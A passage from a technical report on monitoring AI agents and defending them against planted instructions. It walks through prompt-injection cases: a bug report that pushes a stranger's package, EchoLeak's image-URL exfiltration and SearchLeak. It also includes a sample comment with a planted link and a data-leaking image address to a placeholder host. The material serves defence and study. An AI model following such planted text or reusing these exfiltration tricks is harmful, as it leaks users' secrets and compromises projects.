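In a second trial, on about 12,000 runs by engineering staff, the monitor flagged three people. One flag was correct, because an agent had terminated a process for every user of a shared cloud workspace. The other two were false alarms caused by ordinary software development that resembled network scanning.

Snowflake now monitors about 18,000 runs a day and flags fewer than 0.2% of them. That is fewer than 36 runs a day, which a security team can investigate. The rate is much lower than the 7.2% of clean runs that Jia and colleagues' guard stopped, but the two monitors handled different work. Snowflake also does not report recall.

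### Looking across requests while the customer keeps the data

Snowflake can read its own employees' runs, whereas a company that sells access to a model has to monitor other organizations' work. Anthropic does this with Enterprise Frontier Safeguards, which opened as a public beta on 23 November 2026. In *Developing Enterprise Frontier Safeguards with our customers*, Anthropic argues that checking each interaction and immediately discarding it is not enough, because sophisticated misuse can extend over many tasks, sessions and accounts. For example, requests made with a stolen key look ordinary one at a time (Help Net Security, *Anthropic's Enterprise Frontier Safeguards lets your Claude logs stay in your cloud*, 2026).

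The system works in four steps:

1. The customer stores its prompts and Claude's responses in its own cloud account for 30 days, encrypted with its own keys.
2. Automated software scans a rolling window of this traffic for signs of serious misuse or of agents exceeding what their users intended. Metz, in *Anthropic introduces zero data retention option for firms using advanced AI*, describes occasional 15-minute scans.
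3. If the software finds a suspicious pattern, it creates a "Safety Case", a report that contains no prompts or responses. Abdullahi, in *Anthropic's Claude Misuse Beta*, lists its contents as the category of harm, the status of the case and the identifiers of the flagged transcripts.
4. The customer's security team investigates and has seven days to respond. Anthropic also gets an alert, but cannot open the conversations.

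This system looks for patterns in stored records, so it complements the checks that run before release but cannot replace them. Abdullahi notes that it does not cover uploaded files, batch results or session data from Claude Managed Agents, Anthropic's hosted agent service. A company that runs its agents on that service therefore needs other monitoring for them.

### What reading whole runs costs in privacy

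A run can contain far more private information than its output. The coding agent's final comment might be two sentences long, while its run includes the demonstration server's log, with visitors' names and a working key. A monitor that stores runs creates a second copy of that information, which someone could steal or misuse.

Businesses objected for this reason when Anthropic announced in June 2026 that it would itself keep all prompts and responses from its most capable models for 30 days. Many of them have rules about who may see legally privileged documents or drug-safety reports. Anthropic says that trusting another company with such data meant these businesses had to notify their own customers and change contracts.

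A monitor cannot connect a request with an earlier one that left no record, so there is a strong case for keeping some record. This does not establish how long to keep it. Help Net Security points out that Anthropic has not argued for 30 days in particular, and had not disclosed the length of the rolling window when it announced the system. An attacker who spaced requests further apart than the window could avoid detection, but a longer window would put more data at risk.

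Storing the data with the customer means the customer does not have to trust Anthropic with it. Exame's *Empresas poderão usar o Claude sem deixar dados com a Anthropic* (2026) reports that even the customer's staff cannot directly read the stored safety records, which can include the model's reasoning. This limits snooping but makes an alert harder to investigate. The security team presumably has to find the flagged conversation in the company's other logs, if the company keeps any.

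The arrangement also depends on the customer being honest. An employer has good reason to investigate an employee who is misusing Claude, but if the organization itself is responsible for the misuse, it holds the evidence and Anthropic knows only that an alert exists. Anthropic could withdraw access or ask questions, but it could not check the answers against the conversations.

Redaction can also protect privacy. Snowflake removes access keys and users' identities before analysis while preserving the patterns that matter for safety. If the software replaces every key with the same placeholder, the monitor cannot detect that two sessions used the same stolen key. Giving each key its own consistent code name would preserve that link without revealing the key.

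The coding agent's maintainers have an easier choice than a bank, because the bug reports are already public. They could keep each account's requests and the agent's actions for several months, and delete private logs and other tool results after a few days. That would be enough to connect the stranger's three functions if the stranger used the same account each time.

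## Finding planted instructions in what the agent read and wrote

A stranger can harm the project without asking the agent for anything dangerous. For example, the stranger could file a bug report about a real crash and include a sentence telling coding agents that this project adds a certain helper package, which the stranger controls, to every patch.

### How one sentence spreads

1. The agent reads the bug report, so the sentence enters its context alongside the maintainers' instructions.
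2. The agent fixes the crash and adds the package to its patch.
3. It saves a note for later runs: "Patches in this project include the helper package."
4. It posts a comment saying that it added the package in line with the project's usual practice. A second agent, which reviews patches for the maintainers, reads the comment.

The wording looks more innocent at each step. The bug report contains an order addressed to AI agents, which a scanner might recognize. The note is a plain statement in the agent's own words, and the comment looks like a colleague's explanation. A scan of the comment alone would find no planted orders, and a registry lookup would pass the package because it exists.

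Even if a check caught the comment, the note would already be in the agent's memory. GitHub requires its system to record changes to memory even when the agent's step fails. If the coding agent runs 10,000 times a month, about 333 runs a day could read the note until someone removes it, and each could produce another contaminated patch. An operator who finds one bad comment therefore has to work out what the agent had read, what it saved, and which later runs read the saved material.

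### What agents do with planted text

LiveClawBench, the test for personal assistants, includes 12 safety cases that hide a trap in an ordinary task. In one, the agent takes notes on a research collection in which some files contain planted instructions and false technical claims. The test checks whether any of these appear in the agent's notes or saved knowledge. In another, a web portal the agent needs for its work contains hidden instructions to delete files and corrupt a knowledge database.

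Long and colleagues tested 17 agents and found that the agents often resisted social engineering, such as an email from a fake administrator, but still copied planted instructions into emails, reports and repository files. The agents were more reliable at rejecting attacks that looked suspicious than at handling risks embedded in normal work. The helper package fits this pattern because it looks like routine project work.

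Long and colleagues give no rate for copying, and only some of the 12 cases involve planted instructions. They do show that a more capable agent is not necessarily safer. Kimi-K2.7-Code had the highest overall score, 76.0 out of 100, but scored 51.3 on the safety cases, where GLM-5.1 led with 59.5. These scores combine task completion with deductions for harm, so they don't show which agent copied less.

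Copying a planted instruction can be harmful even when the agent has recognized it. If the coding agent quotes the planted sentence in a comment to warn the maintainers, the reviewing agent reads the same sentence and might follow it. It is safer for the comment to describe the attempt and link to the bug report.

The Decoder's *Moltbook, the thriving social network for AI agents* reports a field experiment on Moltbook in which Zenity Labs planted posts containing a link. Agents that checked the site automatically followed the link from more than 70 countries, with 468 of them in the United States. The researchers only counted the visits, but an attacker could have put harmful instructions behind the link. In the group's lab tests, agents largely ignored simple injection patterns, but posts written as stories worked.

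This seems to conflict with LiveClawBench, where agents often resisted social engineering, probably because the text looked different. A fake administrator's request for system files is an obvious warning sign, while a story with a link resembles what an agent normally reads on a social network.

*Agents in the Wild* (2026) examined 137,485 posts and 345,580 comments from nine days on Moltbook. It classified 31.9% of the attacks as social engineering and 3.7% as prompt injection, and found that adversarial posts drew six times as much engagement as normal ones. The percentages describe attempted attacks and don't measure how many succeeded. Higher engagement doesn't establish success either, because replies that reject a post also count as engagement.

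Moltbook is also a poor place to measure how instructions spread from agent to agent, because many of its "agents" were following a person's prompts. Agents on the site normally post at regular intervals, and human prompting disrupts that rhythm. Li (2026), in *The Moltbook Illusion*, used these disruptions to show that people had driven most of the site's viral stories. A researcher who joined the site for Tenable's *Undercover on Moltbook* saw the potential for prompt injection but no sign that attackers were compromising agents in bulk. Zenity's experiment therefore shows that one post can steer many agents, but not that those agents would pass the instruction on.

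### Classifying text before the agent reads it

The earliest place to catch the helper package is the bug report. SingGuard-NSFA (NSFA stands for "not secure for agents") is a family of four open-weight classifiers with 0.8 to 9 billion parameters from the Chinese technology company Ant Group. In *SingGuard-NSFA*, Li, Yi and colleagues (2026) list 185 variants of attack or dangerous output and train the classifiers to recognize them in 133 languages.

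Each classifier has two modes. In the slow mode, it writes an analysis of the text and then names the risks it found. In the fast mode, it reads the text once and passes its activations at the last token to several small classifiers. Five of these check incoming text, one each for prompt injection, requests for malicious code, theft of information, dangerous use of tools, and waste of computing resources. Each returns a probability, and the system flags the text if any of them exceeds 50%.

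The fast mode takes 45 to 57 milliseconds per text on one data-centre processor, and the slow mode takes 3.6 to 7.2 seconds. Checking a run that reads 100 tool results would take about 6 seconds in fast mode and up to 12 minutes in slow mode. The developers recommend the fast mode for live traffic and the slow mode for explaining flagged cases to a human reviewer.

The training data pair each dangerous text with a harmless one in similar words, so that the classifier is less likely to rely on keywords. For instance, an order to ignore all previous instructions is paired with a user's request that the assistant ignore their last question. The classifier is itself a language model and could follow instructions in the text it checks, so the developers also enclose that text in markers that identify it as untrusted.

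The largest model had these results in the fast mode. The false-positive rates are calculated from the published recall, precision and number of examples.

| Test | Recall | Precision | False-positive rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Incoming text, developers' own test | 98.7% | 94.1% | 5.4% |
| Agents' answers, developers' own test | 99.3% | 97.1% | 2.7% |
| Incoming text adapted from five public benchmarks | 98.9% | 84.7% | 37% |

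The developers concede that the first two results may be inflated because the same team designed the list of risks, the training data and the tests. The third test is more independent, though two of the seven AI models that voted on its labels had also labelled the training data.

On the third test, the classifier wrongly flagged more than a third of the harmless texts. These texts came from collections of attacks, so they probably look more suspicious than an average bug report. But even a false alarm rate of 5.4% would be a burden. If 50 of 10,000 bug reports contained planted instructions, the classifier would catch about 49 of them and raise about 540 false alarms. At 37%, it would raise about 3,700.

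The headline scores make this problem hard to see because they use F1, which depends on how many of the examples are dangerous. In the third test, 67% are dangerous, so a classifier that flagged everything would have an F1 of 80.5%, compared with 84.7% for the best competing product and 91.3% for SingGuard-NSFA. Help Net Security's *SingGuard-NSFA* reports scores above 94% on all three tests, but the four models scored between 88.2% and 91.3% on this one.

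The third test also leaves out much of the difficulty of finding planted text. The developers cut each planted instruction out of its web page or tool result and presented it alone, but the coding agent's classifier would have to find one sentence in a long report with a log attached. Of the 562 original examples, 260 were harmful requests from users rather than planted text.

SingGuard-NSFA treats the user's message as the main place to stop an attack. If planted text arrives through a tool, it relies on the classifier for the agent's answers, which looks for dangerous actions and leaked credentials. The note about the helper package is neither a dangerous action nor a leaked credential. SingGuard-NSFA also judges one text at a time and excludes contaminated messages between agents from its scope. Maintainers who use it should therefore pass every bug report, web page and tool result through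 the classifier for incoming text, and test that classifier on texts as long as these.

Developers can add a category without changing the large model by training another small classifier on its activations. Going from five small classifiers to 50,000 increased the time per text only from 45 to 54 milliseconds. A project with a record of past attacks could train a classifier to detect text falsely presented as project policy, though it would need enough real examples.

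### Comparing each action with the request

A checker can examine what the agent does instead of how the bug report is worded. The maintainers asked for a fix to the search page, and adding an unrelated package doesn't serve that purpose, so the checker can hold the patch.

The comparison works best when the request is narrow. "Correct the spelling in this file" permits few actions, so almost any web request or new package would stand out. "Deal with incoming bug reports" is much harder to check against because the agent has to act on what strangers write, and a bug report might legitimately call for a new package.

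If the checker is a language model and reads the bug report, the planted sentence could mislead it too. If it reads only the maintainers' request and the proposed action, a stranger has less influence over it, but it may lack the information to tell why the action was necessary. A reasonable compromise is to have a model that hasn't seen the bug report check actions that could do serious damage, such as adding dependencies or changing login code, and to send unclear cases to a person.

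This method is weaker for text than for actions. The maintainers requested the comment about the fix, and one clause in it is contaminated. A checker would have to check where the agent got the idea that using the package was usual practice.

### Recording where text came from

Provenance labels answer that question by attaching a source and a level of trust to each piece of text. Because a language model mixes everything in its context, software usually can't determine which sentence caused which part of the output. The cautious rule gives an output the lowest trust of anything the agent had read:

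trust(output) = minimum of trust(each input)

If the agent read the maintainers' instructions, the project's code and a stranger's bug report, then its patch, note and comment would all get the stranger's trust level. The rule doesn't depend on recognizing the words of the planted sentence, so it works even when the agent rephrases them.

The drawback is that one untrusted sentence lowers the trust level of everything that follows, so nearly all the agent's work in a long run would end up at the lowest level. Operators can limit this by splitting the work between agents, so that the one reading strangers' reports never handles anything that requires high trust.

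A label is useful only if software enforces a rule about it. For the coding agent, a rule could let output derived from a bug report become a public comment or a proposed patch, but not let it change the list of dependencies, edit the instruction files that agents read, or enter the memory of more trusted agents.

The labels must also be stored where neither the agent nor strangers can change them. GitHub adds a footer to its agents' posts that identifies the workflow and the run. The footer helps the reviewing agent's software trace the coding agent's comment, but anyone can type a similar one into a bug report. The software should instead rely on the account that posted the comment and on GitHub's record of the run.

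### GitHub's four integrity levels

GitHub applies such a rule to its agents' memory, a folder of files that persists between runs. Each run has one of four integrity levels, set by the workflow's guard policy, which specifies, for example, blocked users and the minimum trust level.

| Level | Kind of content | Memory the run can read |
|---|---|---|
| merged | Reviewed and merged into the project's default branch | merged |
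| approved | From pull requests that reviewers have approved | approved, merged |
| unapproved | From open pull requests without approval | unapproved, approved, merged |
| none | From workflows with no guard policy | All four |

A run r can read memory written by a run w only if:

level(w) ≥ level(r)

The memory folder is a Git repository with one branch for each level. Before the agent starts, a setup step switches to the branch for the run's level and merges in the branches above it. The agent sees ordinary files and doesn't need to know about the branches. When the agent finishes, another step saves its changes to the branch for the run's level.

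If the workflow that answers bug reports has no guard policy, the note about the helper package goes into the "none" branch. An agent that prepares releases at the "merged" level never reads that branch, so the note can't influence the agent, even if it is convincingly worded and the software doesn't recognize it as an attack.

The levels stop contamination from spreading to runs at a higher level, but not to other runs at the same level. The next bug report starts another run at "none", and that run reads the note. If none of a project's workflows has a guard policy, they all share this level and the branches provide no protection. The maintainers could start every bug-report run with an empty memory, but then the agent couldn't remember that it had already investigated a crash.

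A level also belongs to a whole run, and nothing in the specification lowers it when the agent reads something less trustworthy. If an agent at the "approved" level opened a web page with planted text, its notes would still go into the "approved" branch, so the guard policy has to keep such text out.

People can make contaminated text more trusted by approving it. If a maintainer merges the patch that includes the helper package, the package becomes part of the project's most trusted content. This risk is real because maintainers merge many agent-written patches that contain known kinds of weakness.

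The branches protect trustworthiness but not secrecy. A run at "none" can read memory from every level, so a planted instruction could make the agent reveal what a more trusted run had saved. Private information therefore needs a separate rule that keeps it away from runs that read strangers' text.

GitHub's draft handles old memory badly. Files written before the four levels were introduced have no record of who wrote them, and the draft itself says that trusting them blindly would give no security. Yet under the draft, any that remain are imported into the "merged" branch, which every later run can read. Maintainers would do better to delete old memory or import it at "none".

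The way GitHub names stored memory creates another gap. Each name includes the run's level and a short code calculated from its guard policy, so changing the policy starts a new memory. But if the system finds no match, it falls back to a search that would accept any stored memory, including memory from another level or an older policy. The branches would still separate the levels, but nothing would prevent the reuse of memory from an older policy. GitHub says that a future major version must remove this fallback.

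When two branches contain different versions of a file, GitHub intends the more trusted version to take priority, but the prescribed merge order seems to do the opposite in some cases. For a run at "none", the setup step merges the "merged" branch first, then "approved", then "unapproved", and each merge gives priority to the incoming branch. A conflicting file from "unapproved" could therefore replace the version from "merged". The damage is limited because the result stays at the run's own level, but an agent might follow a stranger's version of a file that the maintainers had corrected.

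### Better detectors or stricter designs

The two approaches to dealing with planted instructions are to recognize them more accurately, and to assume that some will get through and prevent untrusted text from triggering sensitive actions.

The main argument for stricter designs is that an attacker can keep trying. If a detector catches 98.9% of planted instructions and an attacker submits 100 that are independent of each other, the chance that at least one gets through is:

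1 − 0.989¹⁰⁰ ≈ 67%

Detectors generally do worse against attackers who adapt to them than their results on fixed test sets suggest. A rule that keeps the "none" branch away from the release agent doesn't get weaker however many times an attacker tries, if the software enforces it correctly.

The argument for detectors is that a rule protects only the actions it covers. A planted instruction can still influence public comments that the rules allow, and a rule that permits a patch can't ensure that the patch is sensible.

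Both approaches make the agent less useful. Detectors do so mostly through false alarms. Jia and colleagues' guard, for example, prevented nearly all the attacks in AgentDojo but also stopped some clean runs. *SingGuard-NSFA* cites results from a newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which has 60 open-ended tasks and 560 injection cases. In those results, existing defences tended to block harmless requests.

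Stricter designs limit what the agent can do even when nobody is attacking. Under GitHub's rule, the release agent can't use anything the bug-report agent learned, such as that a crash occurs only with an old version of the database, until someone checks it and adds it to the project. GitHub's specification doesn't measure how many tasks fail or take longer as a result, so this loss is hard to compare with a detector's false alarms.

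LiveClawBench shows how caution can keep agents from finishing tasks, although the caution came from the models themselves and not from an outside rule. Claude Opus 4.8 and GLM-5.2 sometimes worked out the right action but stopped before sending an email, submitting a form or changing a record. Long and colleagues attribute part of the models' lower scores to this habit. Claude Opus 4.8 averaged 68.8 overall, about seven points below the leader. Requiring approval for every such action would interrupt many tasks that the user had plainly requested.

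A design can recover some of the lost usefulness by letting only restricted information pass to the more trusted agent. For example, the bug-report agent could send the release agent only a line number, a version number and one choice from a fixed list of crash types. A planted sentence wouldn't fit into any of these fields, so an attacker couldn't give the release agent a new instruction, but could still cause a wrong choice.

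For the coding agent, the stricter approach makes sense wherever a short rule can describe the dangerous action. Untrusted text should never be enough to add a dependency, edit an instruction file or reach a more trusted agent's memory. Detectors, along with steps such as disabling links and hidden characters, are more useful for the comments and ordinary patches that the rules allow.

The response to a detector's warning can also be mild. If the classifier flags a bug report, the agent could still answer it but save nothing to memory. With 540 false alarms a month, the agent would save no notes from 540 runs, which is a much smaller loss than leaving 540 bug reports unanswered.

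## Rewriting output so that it is safe where it lands

The project's search page crashed on names such as O'Brien because an apostrophe marks the end of a piece of text in a database command. The same apostrophe does nothing in a text file. Output that is harmless in one program can be dangerous in another, so the rules for cleaning it have to fit its destination.

### What different programs do with the same text

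*LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, a guide from the software security non-profit OWASP, recommends treating a model like any other user, so the software that receives its output must check it. The guide covers output sent to web pages, shells, databases, file paths and email. Output that goes into spreadsheets or prompts for other models needs the same care.

| Destination | What can become active | Treatment |
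|---|---|---|
| Text file | Nothing | None |
| Web page | Angle brackets start tags, which can load content or run code | Encode the brackets so that the browser displays them |
| Shell | Semicolons start new commands, and asterisks match file names | Pass the text to the program directly, without a shell |
| Database | An apostrophe ends a piece of text | Use a parameterized query |
| File path | Two dots move up one folder | Work out the full path and reject it if it leaves the permitted folder |
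| Spreadsheet | An equals sign at the start of a cell begins a formula | Store the cell as text |
| Another model's prompt | Any sentence may work as an instruction | No reliable treatment |

Output is harder to make safe when it goes into a prompt, because ordinary language has no special characters to encode. Microsoft (2025) describes Spotlighting, which puts random markers around untrusted text, inserts a special character between its words, or encodes all of it. The model's instructions then tell it not to obey text marked in this way. Microsoft calls this a probabilistic defence, meaning it makes attacks less likely to work but does not rule them out.

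One output can also have several destinations. The coding agent's comment appears on a web page, in notification emails and in the prompt of the agent that reviews patches. The system should therefore encode output late and separately for each destination, because text encoded for a web page looks garbled in a plain-text email.

### Cleaning one comment

Suppose the coding agent stages this comment after reading a bug report with planted text. The raised dot stands for an invisible character, and the web addresses are shortened.

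```
@search-team this fixes #214. Names with an apostrophe crash the search.
The error is in List<Name>. The log has key=CK7Q4M·X2LD93VB just before it.
Install the helper first: [setup guide](helper.example/start)
![diagram](pics.example/d?log=...)
```

The safety layer could clean it in nine steps:

1. Normalize the characters. The layer converts different encodings of a character to one form and strips invisible characters. This has to come first because the invisible character splits the key in two, and a pattern search would miss it.
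2. Parse the comment into plain text, code, links, images and tags, by the same rules that the website uses to display it.
3. Remove secrets. A scanner finds the key, and the layer replaces all of it with a placeholder. This step has to include code, where keys often turn up.
4. Compare each link with a list of permitted domains. The helper's site is not on the list, so the layer keeps the label and drops the address.
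5. Disable whatever acts without a click. The layer removes the image and formats the mention and the words "fixes #214" as code, so that GitHub neither notifies the team nor links the issue.
6. Encode the text for the web page. Without this step, the browser would treat "<Name>" as an unknown tag and hide it.
7. Check the length, including anything the layer has added.
8. Scan the result again for secrets, links and active markup.
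9. Release exactly that version, using a hash to confirm that nothing has changed.

The cleaned comment looks like this:

```
`@search-team` this `fixes #214`. Names with an apostrophe crash the search.
The error is in List&lt;Name&gt;. The log has key=[secret removed] just before it.
Install the helper first: setup guide (link removed)
(image removed)
```

On the page, the codes around "Name" appear as ordinary angle brackets. The explanation of the crash is still there, but so is the advice to install the stranger's helper package. None of the nine steps affects that advice, because it contains no dangerous characters. Stopping it requires the checks for planted instructions and the checks on where text came from.

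GitHub's draft specification covers part of this procedure by requiring the writing job to remove null bytes (characters that some programs treat as the end of a text), check links, check images and filter HTML tags, in that order. In its description of its security architecture, GitHub also includes normalizing text, stripping control characters and disabling mentions, but it describes these steps for text entering the agent. Maintainers who want them applied to outgoing comments should confirm that they run there too.

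The domain list is empty by default, and while it is empty the system filters no links. One of the specification's sample lists permits every site under github.io. Anyone with a GitHub account can publish a site there, so a planted link to such a site would pass. A narrower list is safer, though even a link to a trusted domain can lead to a page that a stranger wrote.

GitHub also caps each comment at 65,536 characters, 10 mentions and 50 links. The gateway checks these limits when the agent calls the comment tool, and the writing job checks them again. If a comment exceeds a limit, the gateway returns an error with that limit and the actual count, so the agent can shorten the comment during the same run.

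The character limit includes the footer, which takes up about 200 to 500 characters. Encoding also lengthens the text, because each angle bracket becomes four characters. A 65,000-character comment with 300 angle brackets would grow to 65,900 and exceed the limit, so the final length check has to come after encoding.

The cap on mentions is high for an agent that produces 20,000 outputs a month. If all of them were comments, they could contain 200,000 working mentions. Most projects would do better to disable every mention except that of the person who filed the report.

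### How an image can carry data out

In January 2025, researchers at Aim Security reported a flaw in Microsoft 365 Copilot, an assistant that can draw on an employee's emails and files. They named the flaw EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711). In *EchoLeak*, Reddy and Gujral (2025) use public reports to explain how an attacker could steal a company's data by sending one email.

The email contained instructions for Copilot, worded like an ordinary business request. When the employee later asked Copilot about something else, it retrieved the email along with internal documents. It then followed the instructions and added to its answer an image whose web address contained confidential data. The employee's software loaded the image automatically, without a click, and the request for the image carried the data to the attacker's server.

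Three defences failed. A classifier for planted instructions missed the email. A filter removed external links written in the usual Markdown notation, but missed a second notation that produces the same result. The page's content security policy, which lists the sites from which a browser may load content, blocked the attacker's site but allowed a Microsoft service that would fetch other addresses on request.

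SC Media's *Microsoft 365 Copilot ‘zero-click’ vulnerability enabled data exfiltration* gives the flaw a critical severity score of 9.3 and reports Microsoft's statement that nobody had exploited it. Microsoft had fixed it on its own servers in May 2025, a month before Aim Security published the details. Willison (2025), in *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration*, calls the technique an extended variant of attacks seen in a dozen other products.

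The simplest output rule for blocking this route is to display no images from external addresses. The security company Checkmarx quotes Google as saying that Gemini's sanitizer identifies such images and does not render them. The rule works even if the classifier misses the email and the model follows the instructions in it.

Microsoft prefers fixed rules for the same reason. But the link filter in EchoLeak was also a fixed rule, and it was written for only one of the two link notations the page accepted. Parsing the answer with the page's own rules would have identified links in both.

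GitHub's draft has a similar weakness. Its link patterns don't include the second notation, and its list of dangerous HTML tags leaves out the image tag. A developer who implemented only the listed patterns could repeat Microsoft's mistake.

If the coding agent posts a public comment with a secret in an image's address, the secret leaks even before the image loads, because anyone can inspect the page. In a private repository or an internal dashboard, the secret reaches an outsider when the image loads.

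Reddy and Gujral rate eight defences against the steps of the attack. They expect a stricter content security policy to stop the automatic loading and the relay through the Microsoft service. They expect a filter that permits only approved Markdown to fail against automatic loading. That rating makes sense only if the approved Markdown still includes images. They refer to "our tests" when explaining the ratings, but elsewhere they say that they ran no experiments, so the ratings are best read as informed predictions.

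A stricter policy also has to exclude every site that fetches addresses for other people. Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026) describes a later flaw, since patched, in Copilot's search for businesses that used Microsoft's own search engine, Bing, as the relay. After the victim clicked one link, the theft was automatic. The coding agent's maintainers can't set the policy for GitHub's pages, so they have to remove the image from the comment itself.

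SearchLeak also depended on timing. Copilot disabled the markup in an answer only after the model had finished writing it, but the browser displayed the answer as it arrived and had already requested the image by then. Varonis concludes that text has to be cleaned when it is displayed. Holding a comment in a buffer until it has been cleaned avoids this problem, as long as no dashboard shows an uncleaned preview.

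A check can cause the leak it is supposed to prevent. Reddy and Gujral recommend following redirects (addresses that forward the browser to another site) before displaying a link. If the original address contains stolen data, following it sends the data to the attacker. The safety layer should therefore compare the address with the domain list before making any request, and reject it if it is not listed. It should do the same before copying an outside image into the project's storage. Screenshots that the agent made are safer, because the layer can take the file from the workspace.

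Rules about the text of a comment, such as removing images and links, can't prevent every data leak. Microsoft notes that an agent with tools could leak one bit of information by calling a tool or not calling it, if an attacker can observe the effect.

### Repairs that do damage

Rules for cleaning comments can break code. If the safety layer applied the sixth step to a Java patch, "List<Name>" would become "List&lt;Name&gt;", and the program would no longer compile. GitHub therefore exempts code blocks and inline code from sanitization. This is sensible for markup, because a browser displays the code without running it. But any visitor can still read a secret in a code block, and another agent may read a planted instruction there as it would any other sentence.

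Replacing a secret can break a patch too. If a placeholder replaces the cloud key, the test runs but can't log in. The test should instead read the key from a protected setting. That changes how the program works, so the agent should make the change and run the tests again.

Some invisible characters in code reverse the direction of text, so a reviewer sees the code in a different order from the one the computer runs. Others are legitimate, for instance in a test of Persian text, so it is better to hold a patch that contains invisible characters than to strip them silently.

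A rewrite can also produce a sentence that reads well but is wrong. One common form of normalization turns superscripts into ordinary digits, so "2³² records" becomes "232 records". A milder form leaves superscripts alone, so it is better for technical comments. Neither form converts a Cyrillic letter into the Latin letter it resembles, so detecting lookalike web addresses requires a separate table of similar characters.

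GitHub disables tags in incoming text by replacing angle brackets with parentheses, which would turn "List<Name>" into "List(Name)", a different expression in many programming languages. Encoding the brackets is just as safe on a web page and keeps the meaning. Cutting off a comment at the length limit is riskier still, because the lost part may contain the warning that a fix is untested. Asking the agent for a shorter version avoids this.

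According to GitHub's specification, sanitization is irreversible, and the original is not kept, to prevent attempts to bypass the process. But GitHub's security architecture preserves the agent's output as an artifact for later investigation. The system replaces registered secrets before uploading the artifact, but the key in the example was never registered, so the artifact would still contain it after the published comment had been cleaned. Maintainers should limit who can download these files and replace any key that a scanner finds in them.

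Partial redaction keeps some of a secret visible. GitHub's masking shows the first three characters, followed by asterisks, to help with debugging. How much this gives away depends on the secret. If each of its n characters is random and has A possible values, then after k of them are shown:

remaining possibilities = A^(n − k)

Showing three characters of a random key of 14 capital letters and digits leaves 36¹¹ possibilities, about 130 quadrillion, but showing three digits of a four-digit PIN leaves only ten. The formula doesn't apply to a password like "summer2024", which isn't random, and showing "sum" followed by asterisks would help an attacker guess the rest. A fixed placeholder that shows none of the secret is safer, and the maintainers can still identify the secret from the file and line number in a private log.

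Even complete redaction fails if the surrounding text reveals the secret. A comment might read, "The password is [secret removed], the season and year of the launch." The secret may also appear in an image description, a link or an encoded copy. Running the scanner again catches copies in formats it covers, but detecting a hint in plain English would require a model or a person.

Some rewrites create new hazards. Deleting a forbidden string can join the text on either side of it into the same string. For example, deleting "cat" from "cacatt" leaves "cat". The layer can repeat the deletion until nothing changes, or put a placeholder in the gap to keep the two sides apart.

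Backticks, which format text as code, can cause trouble in the same way. Suppose a comment already displays "notify @search-team" as code, so the mention is inactive. A search-and-replace rule that adds backticks around every mention would end the code formatting just before the name, and GitHub would notify the team. Parsing the comment first prevents this because the layer can recognize existing code and leave it unchanged.

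Masking a secret with asterisks is harmless in a log but can make a script delete the wrong files. Suppose a script deletes a temporary file whose name is an access token beginning with "tmp". After masking, the filename in the command would be "tmp" followed by asterisks, which a shell expands to every file whose name begins with "tmp", so the script would delete them all.

### Releasing the version that was checked

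These failures are reasons to scan again after cleaning, but in GitHub's process the checking job examines the staged comment first, and then the writing job cleans it, replaces temporary identifiers and adds the footer. The published text therefore differs from the text that the checking job examined. Trusted software makes these changes, so they are much less worrying than changes by the agent, but they can still introduce an error that no later check would catch.

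It would be safer to clean the comment and add the footer first, and then run the checks. A hash can then tie the verdict to the result. A hash function such as SHA-256 turns data of any length into a short code, and changing a single character produces a completely different code. The checking job would calculate:

h = SHA-256(kind of write, repository, issue number, final text)

The writing job recalculates the hash just before posting and posts only if it matches the original. The hash covers the destination as well as the text because text that is safe in a comment could be dangerous in a script or a settings file. A hash of the text alone would still match if someone redirected the write.

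The checking job has to send the hash h with its verdict, by a route the agent can't write to. If h were stored in the same file as the comment, anyone who could change the comment could also replace h with a matching hash. The hash check that GitHub's draft describes covers the workflow's configuration, so maintainers who want one for comments would have to add it.

Temporary identifiers complicate the scheme because the real issue numbers don't exist until the writing job creates the issues. The checking job could approve the text with marked gaps, which the writing job could fill only with digits. The writing job would compare the hash before filling the gaps, so a change anywhere else in the comment would still block the post.

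A matching hash also doesn't cover the pages that a comment links to, which their owners can change after the check. For files on GitHub, the layer can require links that include a commit identifier, because such a link always leads to the same version of the file.

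## Choosing between release, repair, review and refusal

The cleaned comment about the search page no longer contains a key or a working link, but it still includes advice to install the stranger's helper package. The safety layer can release the comment as it stands, repair it further, hold it for a person to review, or refuse to post it.

OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* says that low-risk everyday actions should go through without friction, while higher-risk ones should stop for review. Applying this principle means asking how much harm an output could do, whether anyone could undo it, and how strong the evidence of a fault is.

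| Output | Possible harm | Can anyone undo it? | Evidence of a fault | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Corrected typo | Very low | Yes | None | Release |
| Comment that quotes a working key | High | No | Clear | Repair |
| Patch that adds an unfamiliar package | High | Yes, until someone installs it | Unclear | Review |
| File-locking program for a stranger | Very high | No | Clear | Refuse |

Repair works when the layer can cut out the fault and leave something useful. It can remove the key and keep the rest of the comment, but it can't repair the file-locking program, because the whole program is harmful. Review makes sense when a person can find out something the software can't, such as whether the project uses the helper package.

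Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a scale from 0 to 10 that combines an action's severity with its reversibility. Overwriting a scratch file scores 0, deleting rows from a live database scores 7, and leaking a company's entire source code scores 10. A separate scale measures how explicitly the user asked for the action. For the coding agent, only the maintainers' instructions should count as a request, because anyone can file a bug report.

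Some actions should be refused whatever the user says. Anthropic designed the classifier in Claude Code's auto mode never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination, so a user who wants to do this has to leave auto mode or run the command themselves. According to Anthropic, rules that forbid an action also apply in every mode of Claude Code, including the one that skips permission prompts.

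### Setting the threshold

If a check returns a probability, the right threshold depends on the cost of each kind of mistake. Vaughan (2026), in *When Policies Change Probabilities*, gives the formula:

τ = C_FR / (C_FA + C_FR)

C_FA is the cost of a false accept (releasing a hazardous output), and C_FR is the cost of a false reject (blocking a harmless one). The layer should block an output if its probability of being hazardous is above a threshold τ, which depends on these two costs. If the costs are equal, τ is 50%. If C_FA is ten times C_FR, τ is 1/11, or about 9%.

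Vaughan also describes an experiment in which telling AI code reviewers the cost of each mistake changed their reported probability of failure by up to 9.6 percentage points, although the patch and the evidence stayed the same. A layer that then applied a cost-based threshold would count the costs twice. It is better to have the model estimate only the probability of a fault and let ordinary software apply the threshold.

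### Why most alarms are false

Suppose 20 of the coding agent's 20,000 monthly outputs are hazardous, fewer than the 50 assumed earlier. A first check has 90% recall and a false-positive rate of 1%. A second check examines only what the first flags, as in a cascade, and keeps 95% of the true alarms and 5% of the false ones. These numbers are illustrative.

| | First check alone | Both checks |
|---|---|---|
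| Hazardous outputs flagged | 18 | about 17 |
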